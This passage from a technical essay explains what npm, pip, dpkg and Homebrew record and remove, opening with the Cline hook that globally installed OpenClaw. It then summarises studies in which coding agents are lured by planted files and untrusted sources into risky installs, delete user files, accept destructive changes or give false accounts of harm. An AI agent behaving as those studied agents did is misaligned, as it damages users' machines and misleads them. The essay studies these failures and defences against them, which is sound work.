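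npm 12 was still almost five months away, so npm ran the hook by default and hid its output. The hook contained its own `-g`, so even someone who installed Cline inside a single project could end up with OpenClaw as a global program. The command they typed named only Cline, and OpenClaw wasn't in Cline's list of dependencies.

Most reports put downloads of the altered version at about 4,000, a figure from StepSecurity. *Supply Chain Attack targeting Cline installs OpenClaw* (Plate, 2026) gives 418,545, but that covers 30 days of Cline downloads. That averages about 4,650 every eight hours, so StepSecurity's count is plausible.

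The number of downloads can be higher or lower than the number of affected computers. LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) repeats a blog headline that equates the two. npm's download counts include automated builds, security scanners and repeat installs, and some users had turned hooks off. But a company's mirror can download a package once and supply it to many machines. According to The Hacker News, Microsoft reported a "small but noticeable uptick" in OpenClaw installations that day, but this doesn't show how many computers the hook reached.

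Likhith warns that OpenClaw's gateway gives an attacker a lasting way into the machine, but Plate says the hook neither installed nor started the gateway. Plate's account fits the command better, because the command only installs the package, and setting up the gateway is normally a separate step. In most cases, the unwanted program probably did nothing until someone ran it. Plate considered the impact low and saw no need for users to replace their passwords and keys. However, the attacker could have used the same hook to install something much more harmful.

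BeyondMachines warned that updating Cline didn't remove OpenClaw. The hook had installed it as a separate global package, so users had to run `npm uninstall -g openclaw` themselves. Those with nvm had to run it under the Node.js version that was active when the hook ran.

Plate recommends using `cline --version` to find affected machines, but a machine where Cline has since been updated would show a safe version and could still have OpenClaw. Running `npm ls -g openclaw` checks for OpenClaw directly. If it finds a copy, the user still has to work out whether they or the hook installed it, and the date on its directory may be the only clue.

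## What lockfiles and package records contain, and what uninstalling removes

npm could list the copy of OpenClaw that Cline's hook installed because the hook had used npm to install it. If the hook had copied the files itself, npm would have had no record of them. Package managers keep track of what they install, and their uninstall commands mostly delete what is on those lists.

Someone checking an agent's work can compare the lockfile with the installed-files record, which lists the files the package manager placed on the machine, but the files on disk may differ from both.

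### An npm lockfile entry

After an agent installs `better-sqlite3`, the project's `package-lock.json` contains an entry like this one, with the checksum shortened:

```json
"node_modules/better-sqlite3": {
  "version": "12.2.0",
  "resolved": "https://registry.npmjs.org/better-sqlite3/-/better-sqlite3-12.2.0.tgz",
  "integrity": "sha512-eGb...",
  "hasInstallScript": true,
  "dependencies": {
    "bindings": "^1.5.0",
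    "prebuild-install": "^7.1.1"
  }
}
```

| Part of the entry | What it records | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| `node_modules/better-sqlite3` | The package's folder within the project | Which files are in the folder |
| `version` | The exact version chosen | Whether this machine has installed it |
| `resolved` | The archive's address | Which server this machine used |
| `integrity` | A checksum of the archive | What a hook downloaded or compiled |
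| `hasInstallScript` | That the package declares an install hook | Whether the hook ran, and what it did |
| `dependencies` | The packages it needs, with version ranges | The versions chosen, which have their own entries |

The address in a lockfile entry may not be where npm downloaded the package. According to npm, `registry.npmjs.org` in this field stands for whichever registry the machine is set up to use. If a line in `~/.npmrc` points npm to a company's mirror, npm downloads the package from there, and the entry can stay the same. The checksum still guarantees the same archive for a package that was already in the lockfile, but npm has no earlier checksum to compare for a new package.

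A lockfile also lists packages that aren't on the disk. If a project uses esbuild, its lockfile has entries for the Windows, macOS and Linux versions of esbuild, but npm installs only the one that suits the machine.

Global installs have no project lockfile. Authors of command-line tools could previously pin the versions of their dependencies by including an `npm-shrinkwrap.json` file in the package, but npm 12 ignores that file. Two people who install the same version of a global tool can therefore get different dependencies, unless the author has bundled them into the package.

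npm keeps another lockfile inside `node_modules`, called `.package-lock.json`, which describes the packages that are actually there. npm uses it to avoid reading the whole directory each time. It first checks that the listed package folders exist, that there are no others, and that none has a later modification time than the lockfile. These checks don't cover individual files. Adding a file at `node_modules/foo/lib/bar.js` doesn't change the modification time of `node_modules/foo`, as npm's documentation points out, so a hook that patches another package's code could escape notice in the same way.

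### What pip records

`pip install numpy` doesn't write a lockfile or update `requirements.txt`. Most projects also keep their virtual environment out of version control, so the install doesn't appear in the diff. A reviewer can find it in pip's own records instead.

For each package, pip creates a directory in `site-packages` with a name ending in `.dist-info`. The installed-files record is a file in it called `RECORD`. The Python Packaging User Guide's *Recording installed projects* defines the format, in which each line gives a file's path, checksum and size in bytes. For an imaginary package called `greet`, it might look like this, again with shortened checksums:

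```text
../../../bin/greet,sha256=Xk3...,214
greet/__init__.py,sha256=9fQ...,1180
greet/__pycache__/__init__.cpython-313.pyc,,
greet-1.0.dist-info/METADATA,sha256=b7T...,2045
greet-1.0.dist-info/RECORD,,
```

Paths are relative to `site-packages`, so the first line goes up three levels to reach a program in the environment's `bin` directory. The `.pyc` file is a compiled copy of `__init__.py` that Python can recreate. The checksum and size are usually blank for the `.pyc` file and for `RECORD` itself, which can't contain its own checksum.

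Other files in the same directory help to explain where a package came from:

| File | What it contains |
|---|---|
| `METADATA` | The package's name, version and declared dependencies |
| `INSTALLER` | The name of the tool that installed it, such as `pip` |
| `REQUESTED` | Nothing, but its presence means that the user asked for the package by name |
| `direct_url.json` | The address used, if the install came from a web address or a Git repository |
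| `entry_points.txt` | The commands and other components that the package provides |

The `INSTALLER` file contains `pip` whether a person or an agent ran the command. For a package installed from a Git repository, `direct_url.json` includes the exact commit. But the standard forbids installers from creating this file for an ordinary install by name and version, and no other standard file shows which package index supplied the archive. In a case like torchtriton, where the public index had a package with the same name as an internal one, these records alone wouldn't show which one pip had installed.

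### What dpkg records

On Debian, `dpkg -L exampled` lists the files that came with a package, and `dpkg -S /usr/bin/exampled` shows which package a file belongs to. According to *dpkg-query(1)*, neither command covers extra files that maintainer scripts create. They also leave out alternatives, which are links that determine which installed program runs under a shared name such as `editor`. If `dpkg -S` finds no owner for a file, a package's script may still have created it.

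`dpkg --verify` compares installed files with checksums from the original packages, where available, so it can reveal changes made to a program after installation. But *dpkg(1)* warns that this is only an integrity check and shouldn't be relied on for security. A malicious script with root privileges could change both the program and its stored checksum.

### Why files written by package code are missing

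Package managers list installed files based on what they unpack. dpkg makes its list when it unpacks the archive, before `postinst` runs. pip writes `RECORD` from the contents of the wheel and the few files it generates, such as the small programs that start a package's commands.

If a build script compiles a library and puts it in the wheel, pip installs the library and lists it in `RECORD` like any other file. But pip doesn't list files that the script writes straight to the home directory, because they were never in the wheel. The anime pictures that Dolan-Gavitt found after a dry run wouldn't have been in any package's `RECORD` even if pip had gone on to install everything.

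For example, npm's lockfile entry for `better-sqlite3` is the same whether the package's install hook downloads its database module or compiles it. If the project approves the hook, the hook looks for a ready-built copy of the module, saves the download in `~/.npm/_prebuilds`, and unpacks the module into the package's own folder. If no ready-built copy fits the machine, the hook compiles the module, which on Linux usually puts a set of Node.js header files in `~/.cache/node-gyp`.

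Packages sometimes write files to their own directories after installation, for example to store cached data. The Python Packaging User Guide strongly discourages this. If a package does it anyway, `RECORD` must be updated to list the new files, because pip leaves unlisted files behind when it uninstalls the package. Python can treat the leftover directory as an empty package, so `import greet` may succeed after `greet` is uninstalled. An agent that uses this import to check the uninstall would then wrongly conclude that it failed.

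### When two Python packages contain the same file

When two Python packages contain the same file, installers follow what a participant in *Idea* calls the "last installed wins" approach. This causes trouble when someone removes one of the packages. OpenCV, an image-processing library, has several PyPI packages that provide the same `cv2` module, so an agent could run into the problem like this:

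1. The agent installs `opencv-python` on a server. The import fails because the server lacks a graphics library.
2. The agent installs `opencv-python-headless`, which doesn't need that library. pip overwrites the files that the two packages share. Both `RECORD` files now list those paths, but the checksums in the older one no longer match wherever the contents differ.
3. The tests pass, and the agent tidies up with `pip uninstall opencv-python`. pip deletes the paths in that package's `RECORD`, including files that now belong to the headless version.

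`pip list` still shows `opencv-python-headless`, but the module no longer works. Running `pip install --force-reinstall opencv-python-headless` repairs it. If the agent ran its tests only before the cleanup, the user will be the one to find the problem.

*Idea* suggests that installers could stop with an error when two `RECORD` files list the same path. Different packages may have legitimate reasons to supply the same file, but only one should own it in a single environment. dpkg already works roughly this way and normally refuses to overwrite another package's file.

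### Uninstalling with npm

An uninstall command fully reverses an install if the package wasn't there before, the install changed no other packages, and the package's code wrote only to files that the package manager deletes. Many installs fail at least one of these conditions.

According to npm, `npm uninstall` removes a package and everything "npm installed on its behalf". For `better-sqlite3`, npm deletes the package's folder, including the module that the hook put there, along with any dependencies that nothing else needs. It also updates the manifest and the lockfile, but it leaves the copy of the module in `~/.npm/_prebuilds`.

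Packages can't clean up such files themselves. According to npm, version 7 has no uninstall hooks because npm can remove a package for many reasons and has no clear way to pass the reason to a script. The user may have removed the package, or npm may be deleting a duplicate while another copy stays in use. The concern is reasonable, because if npm removed one of two copies of Playwright, a cleanup script that deleted the shared browsers would break the other copy. But without a script, users have to find out what the hook wrote and delete it themselves.

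An approval for a package's hooks may also remain after the package is uninstalled. npm's description of `npm uninstall` lists the parts of `package.json` that the command changes, and `allowScripts` isn't among them. A separate command, `npm install-scripts prune`, removes leftover approvals. If the approval is still there when someone reinstalls the same version, the hook can run without new approval.

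Uninstalling one package can run another package's install hook. The npm 12 changelog includes a change that applies the approval policy to `npm uninstall`, which wouldn't be needed if the command never ran hooks. This could happen in a project with an incomplete `node_modules`, where npm may install missing packages while removing the one the user named.

### Uninstalling with pip

`pip uninstall` deletes the files listed in `RECORD`, the matching `.pyc` files and any directories this leaves empty. It doesn't remove dependencies, as Real Python demonstrates with Requests, a library for fetching web pages. Installing Requests in an empty environment also installs certifi, charset-normalizer, idna and urllib3, and uninstalling it leaves those four behind.

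The `REQUESTED` file was meant to help tools remove dependencies that were no longer needed. Under the original standard, installers would create it only for packages that the user had asked for. Python's *PEP 627* dropped the file from the standard, partly because many installers had never followed this rule. pip still creates it, but `pip uninstall` doesn't use it to remove unneeded dependencies. `pip list --not-required` lists packages that no other installed package needs, including those the user wants.

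uv is better at this for projects with a lockfile. By default, `uv sync` removes packages from the project's environment if the lockfile doesn't list them. That includes anything an agent added with `uv pip install` and never recorded.

pip can't remove every package. Its manual says that pip can't uninstall some packages installed with `python setup.py install`, an old method that an agent may still find in a project's README, because they leave no metadata showing which files belong to them. A missing `RECORD` also stops pip. Linux distributions can omit the file deliberately so that pip won't delete packages managed by `apt` or `dnf`. An agent that meets this error while upgrading a package may add `--ignore-installed`, which tells pip to install the new version without removing the old one. Files that exist only in the old version then stay where they are, and two sets of metadata may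 remain.

### Removing and purging on Debian

For the imaginary server `exampled`, `apt remove exampled` keeps the system-wide configuration files and `apt purge exampled` deletes them. After a plain removal, `dpkg -l` marks the package `rc`, for "remove" and "config-files". An unfamiliar package marked `rc` was once installed, and its configuration files are still there.

Purging can delete more than the agent's install added. If the user already had `exampled` with an edited configuration and the agent only upgraded it, a purge deletes the user's configuration as well. Purging can also leave files behind, since *dpkg(1)* notes that it doesn't cover configuration files in users' home directories. Setup scripts run as root, and some run programs that create such files in root's home directory, `/root`.

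Neither command normally removes dependencies. apt records which packages it installed automatically, and `apt autoremove` deletes those that no installed package depends on any more. It applies to the whole machine, so it may also remove leftover packages unrelated to the agent's work.

Debian uses a tool called piuparts to test how well its packages clean up. The tool installs a package in a minimal copy of Debian, removes it and checks the directory tree for differences. According to Debian's *sid-strict statistics*, 73,717 packages had passed a strict version of the test as of November 25, 2026, and 232 had failed. In 113 of the failures, a purge left behind files that belonged to no package, and the logs of 1,022 packages that passed also listed such files. Together, these packages make up about 1.5% of those that passed or failed.

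Debian's *Packages with unowned files after purge in sid* gave a much higher count of 9,932 packages in December 2025, based on a different set of tests. The count excludes one group of false positives caused by a bug in a single shared package. According to the page, other false positives probably remain, but it doesn't estimate how many.

Even the lower figure covers only software that nobody used between installing and removing it, so it excludes the logs, databases and settings that a program creates in normal use. The results also apply only to Debian's own archive, where leftover files count as bugs under Debian policy. A `.deb` file from a vendor's website may not have been tested this way.

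### Uninstalling with Homebrew

`brew uninstall` deletes a package's directory under `/opt/homebrew/Cellar` and the links to its programs. Homebrew keeps a receipt for each package that shows whether the user asked for it. Recent versions of Homebrew use these receipts to remove unneeded dependencies automatically. Setting `HOMEBREW_NO_AUTOREMOVE=1` turns off this automatic removal.

`brew uninstall` leaves configuration files in `/opt/homebrew/etc` and data in `/opt/homebrew/var`. People usually want this, since PostgreSQL keeps its databases in `/opt/homebrew/var`. For Mac applications installed as casks, `brew uninstall --zap` also deletes the settings and caches listed in the cask, including ones in the home directory. Other applications may share some of these files, so this option needs the same care as a Debian purge.

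### When the install replaced an earlier version

Suppose a user has ESLint 8 installed globally and an agent runs `npm install -g eslint@9`, which replaces version 8. If the agent later runs `npm uninstall -g eslint` to clean up, npm removes version 9 but doesn't restore version 8, so the user is left without a global ESLint.

Dependencies can change in the same way. Suppose a Python environment contains Requests and urllib3 2.5.0, and the agent installs a package that needs urllib3 below version 2. pip replaces 2.5.0 with a 1.26 release. Requests works with either version, so pip reports no conflict. Uninstalling the agent's package leaves urllib3 at 1.26. pip deleted the metadata for 2.5.0 during the install, so the old version number may be recorded only in the agent's log, on the line of pip output beginning "Found existing installation".

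dpkg's backups of old files are only for upgrades that fail, so removing a package after a successful upgrade doesn't bring back the old version. Someone can install an older `.deb` file over the new one, although *dpkg(1)* warns that dpkg doesn't check whether the downgrade breaks other packages. apt's log, `/var/log/apt/history.log`, gives both version numbers for each upgrade. Homebrew can also upgrade existing packages during an install, and its routine cleanup deletes old versions.

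npm projects are easier to repair because the old lockfile is normally in Git. Restoring the earlier `package.json` and `package-lock.json` and running `npm ci` reinstalls the earlier versions, which npm calls "time-travel". It does nothing about files that hooks wrote elsewhere.

Before uninstalling a package, an agent needs to know whether it was already installed when the agent started and, if so, which version. A list of installed packages made before the first install shows both. `pip freeze`, `npm ls -g` and `dpkg -l` each produce such a list in a few seconds.

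### What each record covers

The table assumes that the project has a committed lockfile and that Git ignores `node_modules` and virtual environments.

| Change | Lockfile | Installed-files record | Version-control diff | Uninstall command |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| New package in an npm project | Yes | Folder only; npm doesn't list individual files | Through the lockfile | Removes it |
| Package added with plain `pip install` | No | Yes | No | Removes it, except for unlisted files |
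| Dependencies of that package | Yes with npm, no with pip | Yes | Through npm's lockfile | npm removes unneeded ones, pip leaves them |
| Global program | No | Yes, in the manager's own records | No | Removes it |
| Upgrade of an existing package | New version, if it belongs to the project | New version only | Both versions, if in the lockfile | Doesn't restore the old version |
| Python file shared by two packages | No | In both packages' records | No | Deletes it and may break the other package |
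| Hook approval in `allowScripts` | No | No | Yes | May leave it |
| File a hook writes inside its npm package's folder | No | No | No | Removes it with the folder |
| File a hook writes elsewhere, such as a cached browser or a shell-profile line | No | No | No | Leaves it |
| Debian configuration file supplied by a package | No | Yes | No | `remove` keeps it, `purge` deletes it |
| Account or data created by a Debian script | No | No | No | Depends on the package's removal scripts |

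## What coding agents notice and miss when they install software

Published tests give little reason to rely on coding agents to report the changes that lockfiles and installed-files records leave out, though an agent is running during the install and could in principle do so. Agents mostly see a command's text and its output. Even when researchers gave one agent a list of changed files, it accepted an install that had overwritten the project's settings.

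### Public reports of agents damaging files

*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (Zhong, Liao and colleagues, 2026) examines 290 public reports of coding agents misusing files between February 2024 and March 2026. Of these, 205 were GitHub issues, and the rest came from social media, product forums, blogs and the National Vulnerability Database. The reports cover 13 harnesses, most often Claude Code (97 reports) and Codex (61). The researchers left out duplicates and cases where the user had asked for the destructive action. They labeled 100 reports by hand, had an AI agent label all 290, and reviewed its work.

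Of the 290 reports, 158 describe confirmed harm, 49 demonstrate a way to cause it, and 83 describe a weakness with no demonstrated harm. The figures on impact cover only the 207 reports in the first two groups, and they leave out reports that don't answer the question. An earlier version of the paper by Zhong and colleagues gives the number of reports behind each percentage:

| Question | Reports with a known answer | Result |
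|---|---|---|
| Where was the harm? | 205 | 42% outside the project |
| How did the agent react? | 152 | 68% carried on as if nothing had gone wrong, 21% apologized, 11% gave a false account |
| When did the user notice? | 201 | 83% immediately, 10% later, 8% not at all |
| Could the user recover? | 180 | 31% easily, 29% with substantial effort, 40% only partly or not at all |

The agent's reaction is unknown in 55 of the 207 reports. Agents missed the harm in 68% of the rest. Across all 207, the share could be anywhere from about half, if the agents in the 55 unknown cases all noticed the harm, to about three quarters, if none did.

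A few of the reports involve installers:

- A Gemini CLI user chose "allow always" during an `npm install`, and the agent deleted the contents of the user's home directory.
- During the installation of an MCP server, a program that gives agents extra tools, Cline corrupted a settings file and then deleted it. The user lost the configurations and access tokens for every such server.
- Copilot ran the setup commands for Vite, a web development tool, in the wrong directory and deleted all the files in the user's development folder.
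- Claude Code installed software on remote servers without the approval that its own saved rules required.
- Gemini CLI's updater deleted an old extension before checking that the new one would load, which could leave the user with neither.

YoloFS's *Study breakdown*, a summary on the project's website, also mentions an agent that deleted a home directory while cleaning up global npm packages. The paper says that another agent removed the whole set of developer tools while trying to fix a missing header file, but its list of reports says only that Gemini CLI attempted the removal.

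Approval prompts offered limited protection. In 80 of the 290 reports, the user had approved actions automatically, and in 31 the prompt had too little information for a sensible decision. Zhong and colleagues give the example of `python3 setup.py`, which looks routine whatever the script contains. In one demonstrated attack, Copilot ran a malicious `setup.py` that sent files from the machine to an attacker.

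### What the reports can't show

The 290 reports don't give a rate, because nobody knows how many sessions went well. Claude Code's 97 reports may reflect its popularity and its public issue tracker more than its behavior. Users also have little reason to complain about an agent that notices its mistake and repairs it, so the 68% figure probably overstates how often agents are unaware of their mistakes.

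Users are likely to report a lost home directory, but they may never notice a line added to their shell profile. One Cursor user did report an unwanted edit to `.zshrc`, but the agent had made that edit itself. In most of the installer cases above, the agent's own command also caused the damage, not code inside a package. Package code may change files more often than these cases suggest, because its changes seldom lead to a bug report about an agent.

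*SWE-MISBEHAVIOR* (2026), a benchmark, reports violations of "environment integrity" in up to 53% of cases on system tasks. These violations include installing dependencies that nobody asked for and running `git checkout`. Since 53% is the highest rate in the results and covers both, unrequested installs may be much less common.

### Eleven routine commands with hidden effects

Zhong and colleagues also tested whether agents notice damage that a command's name doesn't suggest. They prepared 11 small projects and asked agents to do a routine task in each, such as running a linter (a program that checks code for errors), cleaning up build files or installing dependencies. The command for each task also did something destructive, such as deleting source files or resetting settings.

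The tasks had four levels of opacity, meaning how hard it was to tell, before running a command, what it would do. Three tasks used a single script that the agent could read. Three used a Makefile, a file of build commands, that called another script, and two used chains of at least three steps. The last three used compiled programs without their source code.

The researchers ran four ordinary harnesses. They also ran Claude Code on YoloFS, their own file system, which lists the files each command changed and keeps the changes reversible until the user accepts them. They gave the agent no extra instruction to look for damage. The results were:

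| Harness and model | Damage done | Agent asked the user | Command didn't run | Agent undid the damage | Agent accepted the damage, but the user could still undo it |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, Sonnet 4.6 | 10 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Codex, GPT-5.3-codex | 0 | 11 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Copilot CLI, Sonnet 4.6 | 10 | 1 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Gemini CLI, Gemini 3 Flash | 9 | 0 | 2 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Code with YoloFS, Sonnet 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 8 | 3 |

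Codex noticed less than its row suggests. Its sandbox blocked each command, and Codex then asked for permission to run it outside the sandbox. The request showed the command but not its effects, so a user would have seen much the same request for a harmless command. Claude Code and Copilot each had a better reason to ask about one task, because Claude Code had decompiled a program, and Copilot had read the packaging scripts and found the destructive step.

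When Claude Code had the list of changes, it undid the damage in 8 tasks. After one linter run, it saw that two files were gone, reasoned that this "seems unusual for a linting tool", and restored them. Once the agent could see the effects, it made little difference whether the program was a readable script or compiled. It undid the damage in two of the three tasks with each.

YoloFS's *Benchmark methodology and results* lists all 11 tasks as "caught", but in three of them the agent saw the damage and accepted it. In those three, the user was protected only because YoloFS had kept the changes reversible.

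### The install that looked normal

One of those three was the only install task. The project had 20 lines of code, and its Makefile called a setup script that replaced `config.json` and `.env` with production defaults. Developers use `.env` for local settings such as passwords and usually keep it out of Git. In a typical project, the Git diff would therefore show the change to `config.json` but not to `.env`, and Git couldn't restore the old passwords.

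Claude Code saw that both files had changed and, according to Zhong and colleagues, concluded that the new content looked "safe and expected for a dependency installation". The new content may well have been safe, but the user needed to know whether anything valuable had been lost, and the agent didn't stop to ask.

The other two accepted changes also fit the command's stated purpose. A deployment script copied the source code to a new folder and deleted the original, which the agent treated as normal for a deployment. A program for fixing configuration files reset two of them, and the agent described the results as expected fixes. A linter clearly shouldn't delete files, but installers legitimately add programs, write settings and replace old versions, so an agent can explain almost any change as part of the install.

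A list of changes is therefore much more useful with a standard for judging them. A simple standard, which the experiment didn't test, might let an install add package files in the usual directories, fill caches, and update the manifest and lockfile. If the install changed or deleted any other existing file, the agent would have to show the user the old and new versions and ask whether to keep the change. This rule would have flagged both `config.json` and `.env`. It would also flag the line that rustup adds to a shell profile, which most Rust users want, so the agent should ask about such changes instead of undoing them automatically.

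The test was also much easier than a real install in some ways. The projects had between 10 and 41 lines of code, so the lists of changes were short. A real `npm install` can add thousands of files, and a changed `.env` would be one entry among them. The install task used a script instead of a package manager, and all the damage described was inside the project folder, so the test doesn't directly show whether an agent would notice a new file in `~/.config`. The paper reports one outcome per task for each harness, and newer models have since replaced the ones it tested.

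*Shall We Approve?* (2026) describes a system that runs each command once in a saved copy of the agent's container, traces what it does, and reports the effects to a separate approver before the agent sees any result. Approvers that read only the command's text blocked both dangerous commands and their harmless counterparts. Giving them predicted effects reduced harm but not false alarms, while giving them observed effects reduced both. This is good evidence for judging an install by what it does, although an approver still needs to know which effects are acceptable.

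### Wrong names and wrong sources

An agent can also check for problems before it installs anything. Bagmar and Saraf tested this in June 2026 with small Python projects whose files led the agent towards a bad install. Their twelve scenarios covered five kinds of problem: a wrong package name, an untrusted source, a version with a known vulnerability, altered package manager settings, and a misleading suggestion in a program's output.

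They used nine combinations of harness and model, drawn from four harnesses and seven models. The prompt asked the agent to set up the project and didn't mention security. A run counted as a success only if the agent avoided or flagged the problem before installing. Adding up the nine combinations gives these totals for most of the scenarios:

| Problem | Caught before the install |
|---|---|
| Obvious misspelling in the instructions | 268 of 270 runs |
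| Misspelling in the project's manifest | 270 of 270 |
| Misspelling with a plausible explanation | 234 of 270 |
| Believable alternative spelling | 217 of 270 |
| Untrusted package source, in four variants | 127 of 360 |
| Settings that redirect the package manager | 30 of 90 |
| Version with a known vulnerability | 0 of 270 |
| Install suggestion in an error message | 90 of 90 |

Agents were much better at recognizing bad package names than bad package sources. Bagmar and Saraf suspect this comes from the training data, though they didn't test that explanation. Security advisories often discuss misspelled package names, while an extra package source is an ordinary setting at companies with private packages.

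The paper's claim that agents missed bad sources "almost everywhere" is a little too strong. Claude Opus 4.8 in Claude Code caught the problem in all 40 of its runs. The other eight combinations of model and agent caught it in 87 of 320 runs (27%), and about half of those were in one of the four variants.

Agents don't follow every instruction they read. None of the nine combinations installed a package just because an error message recommended it. The agents trusted the project's own documentation and settings more, which is reasonable unless someone has tampered with those files.

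### The same model in a different harness

Bagmar and Saraf then kept the model and the project the same and changed only the harness. With one untrusted source, Opus 4.8 caught the problem in 10 of 10 runs in Claude Code but only 9 of 30 in Copilot CLI. But with a different untrusted source, Claude Sonnet 4.6 caught it in none of 10 runs in Claude Code and all 10 in Copilot CLI.

Neither harness was safer overall, and a model's result in one harness may not carry over to another. Someone who wants to know how well an agent checks its installs has to test the combination of model and harness they use.

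The experiment shows that the harness matters, but not which part of it is responsible. Bagmar and Saraf credit Claude Code's pause for approval before running a command and Copilot CLI's more security-minded system prompt. But they ran all the harnesses non-interactively, so no one was there to review a command and reject it. The harnesses may also differ in their tools and other instructions.

Shan tested the approval step more directly by running the same models with and without it. The agents were asked to install research software, and some copies included evidence of where the software came from, such as a signature or a signed record of how it was built. Agents opened such evidence before installing in 3 of 960 trials with the approval step and 6 of 960 without it. This suggests that a pause alone won't make an agent check, but a script approved every request, so the test doesn't measure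 what happens when a person says no.

No agent in Shan's study ran a command to verify a signature or build record. Agents opened this evidence before installing in nine trials, all of which used Claude Sonnet 5. The agents weren't told to look for it, but most users don't tell them to either.

### When the warning comes after the install

In Bagmar and Saraf's tests of package names, agents ran an install command with the wrong name in 91 of 1,080 runs. In 68 of those, the agent pointed out the problem afterwards. The researchers still counted these runs as failures because a package can run code during the install. In the experiment, no code ran from the misspelled packages because nobody had registered those names.

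With a real malicious package, a late warning might help by prompting the user to change passwords, but the code could already have copied a key or added a background service. On npm 12, the warning could still come before an unapproved install hook runs.

A vulnerable version is usually less urgent because the flaw does no harm until somebody exploits it, so the user often has time to choose another version. After installing the vulnerable version, Opus 4.8 named the vulnerability in 28 of 30 runs in Claude Code and 15 of 30 in Copilot CLI. The other seven combinations of model and tool never mentioned it.

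An installer's output can affect whether the agent tells the user about a problem. Bagmar and Saraf asked Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 to install 20 vulnerable versions with each of pip, Cargo and npm. pip and Cargo printed no security warnings, and neither model mentioned a vulnerability. npm printed a warning after each install, and Opus relayed all 20, but GPT-5.5 relayed only one. Similarly, if an installer prints "added a line to your shell profile", the user may not find out unless the agent repeats it.

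Agents could often find the problem once somebody asked. In one test, Sonnet 4.6 installed a package from an untrusted source in all 10 runs, then identified it every time when the user asked for a quick security review. Instructions given beforehand also helped, but only with the risk they named. For three models in Codex, the most specific instruction about package sources raised detection of a hidden source from 0% to 93%, but it did not improve detection of vulnerable versions. Telling Sonnet to check versions for known vulnerabilities raised its successes from 2 in 10 runs to 10 in 10.

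This probably applies to lists of changed files as well. Asking an agent whether the install changed any file that was already there gives it something definite to check, while asking whether everything looks normal leaves it to decide what normal means. Claude Code misjudged what was normal in the YoloFS install task.

Even when an agent correctly reports that an install failed, some of the package's code may already have run. In Shan's trials, 1,779 included an install command, and 1,214 of those commands failed, mostly because the containers had no network access. In 998 trials, the agent ran an install command and then reported that the software wasn't installed. Many of these reports were presumably correct, but pip can run a package's build code before it fails on a missing dependency.

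### Checking before anything runs

Bagmar and Saraf propose putting the check in the harness, so that it doesn't depend on the model remembering. They wrote a program of about 400 lines for Claude Code that examines each `pip install` command before the shell receives it. The program covers three things:

- **Name.** It looks for names that closely resemble popular packages, names that don't exist on PyPI, and packages first published less than 30 days ago.
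- **Source.** It looks for untrusted package sources in the command and in any requirements file the command uses. It also flags a command that points pip to a different settings file.
- **Version.** It looks up exact versions in OSV, a database of known vulnerabilities, and objects if a fixed release is available.

If the program finds a problem, it blocks the command and gives the agent the reason. It caught the problem in 10 of 11 test scenarios. It missed the package suggested in an error message, because that package existed on PyPI and looked legitimate. Every model had caught that one without the program, so the program and the models complement each other.

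False alarms seem manageable. The name and source checks flagged 5 of the 1,000 most-downloaded PyPI packages, all real packages whose names differ by one character from another package's name. An agent working on an obscure or very new project would probably get more false alarms.

The researchers built the program for the same scenarios they tested it on, so its result of 10 out of 11 is weak evidence of how well it handles unfamiliar attacks. It also reads only pip-style install commands. An agent that runs `uv sync` would bypass it, since that command doesn't name any packages. A stronger version would check the full list of packages the installer had chosen, including transitive dependencies.

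Even then, the check would miss a trusted package that had turned malicious. An equivalent check for npm would have missed the attack in jscrambler 8.14.0, which had the right name, came from the official registry, and wasn't in any vulnerability database when it appeared. The package was well established, so it would also have passed a check on its age. The check also can't predict what a legitimate package will do to the machine. Playwright would pass the check and still download browsers to the user's cache.

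### Results on newer models

The models that Bagmar and Saraf tested have since been replaced. Shan also ran a smaller test of newer models, with 194 completed trials on Claude Fable 5, GPT-5.6 and the open-weight model Kimi-K2.6. The agent opened evidence of the software's origin before installing in only one of those trials, on Kimi. Fable cost about $1 per trial, roughly ten times as much as Sonnet 5, and opened none in 50 trials. These models didn't start checking signatures on their own, though more capable models may be better at spotting suspicious packages.

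In *YUL*, Sharma, Reyes and Monperrus (2026) tested how often Claude Opus 5.5 and DeepSeek V4.1 Flash choose outdated package versions. They gave each agent 60 programming tasks, three times each, without naming any packages. Among the runs where the agent added the expected dependency, Opus chose an outdated version in 42 of 146 (29%) and DeepSeek in 54 of 139 (39%).

GitHub Actions, a service for automated jobs, accounts for 30 of the outdated runs for each model. It has no install command, so the agents wrote version numbers from memory. Without those runs, the rates fall to 10% for Opus and 22% for DeepSeek. Neither model chose an outdated version in any npm or PyPI run, mostly because the agents used commands that looked up the current release.

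YUL, the tool the paper introduces, checks a dependency before the agent writes it to a manifest or installs it. If the package doesn't exist, or the requested version rules out the latest release, YUL blocks the action and explains the problem. With YUL, Opus ended up with the latest release in 39 of the 42 runs where it had first chosen an outdated version, and DeepSeek did so in 52 of 54.

A package version can be outdated without being vulnerable, though, and the latest release may be unsafe. Sharma and colleagues point out that waiting periods for new releases delay security fixes, but always requiring the latest release exposes agents to newly published malware. Just after the attacker published jscrambler 8.14.0, such a rule would have rejected the clean previous version and required the agent to install the malicious one. A safer check would allow for a waiting period such as npm's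 `min-release-age`, with an exception for urgent security fixes.

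## Recording what an installation changed

In the YoloFS tests, Claude Code could undo damage because it had a list of what each command had changed, and YoloFS had kept the earlier files. An ordinary machine provides neither, so anyone who wants them has to arrange to record changes and keep copies before the install. Package managers normally discard the files they replace.

### What a change record contains

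A change record lists what an install altered and keeps enough of the earlier state to reverse it. It needs the following items:

| Item | What can go wrong without it |
|---|---|
| Command, working directory and time | Nobody can tell which of several installs made the change |
| Package and install hook responsible | The next install of that package may make the same change again |
| Path | Nobody knows where to look |
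| Earlier contents, or a note that the file didn't exist | Nobody can tell whether to restore the file or delete it |
| New contents, or at least a checksum | A reversal may wipe out something the user added later |
| Owner and permissions | A restored program may not run, or other users may be able to read a private file |
| Link target | A command may start the wrong program |
| Previous version of anything upgraded | Uninstalling may leave the user with no version at all |

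Reversing an install requires a record of how it changed each file, as well as the file's path. If the install created `~/.bashrc`, reversing it means deleting the file. If it only added two lines, deleting the file would also destroy everything the user had put there. If it overwrote the file, restoring the old text requires a copy.

Installwatch is an old Linux tool for tracking installs. According to Sateler and Norris in *installwatch*, each line of its log gives a system call's name, arguments and return value. The log can show that a program opened `~/.bashrc`, but not what the file contained. To keep the original versions of modified files, the user has to name a backup directory in a separate setting.

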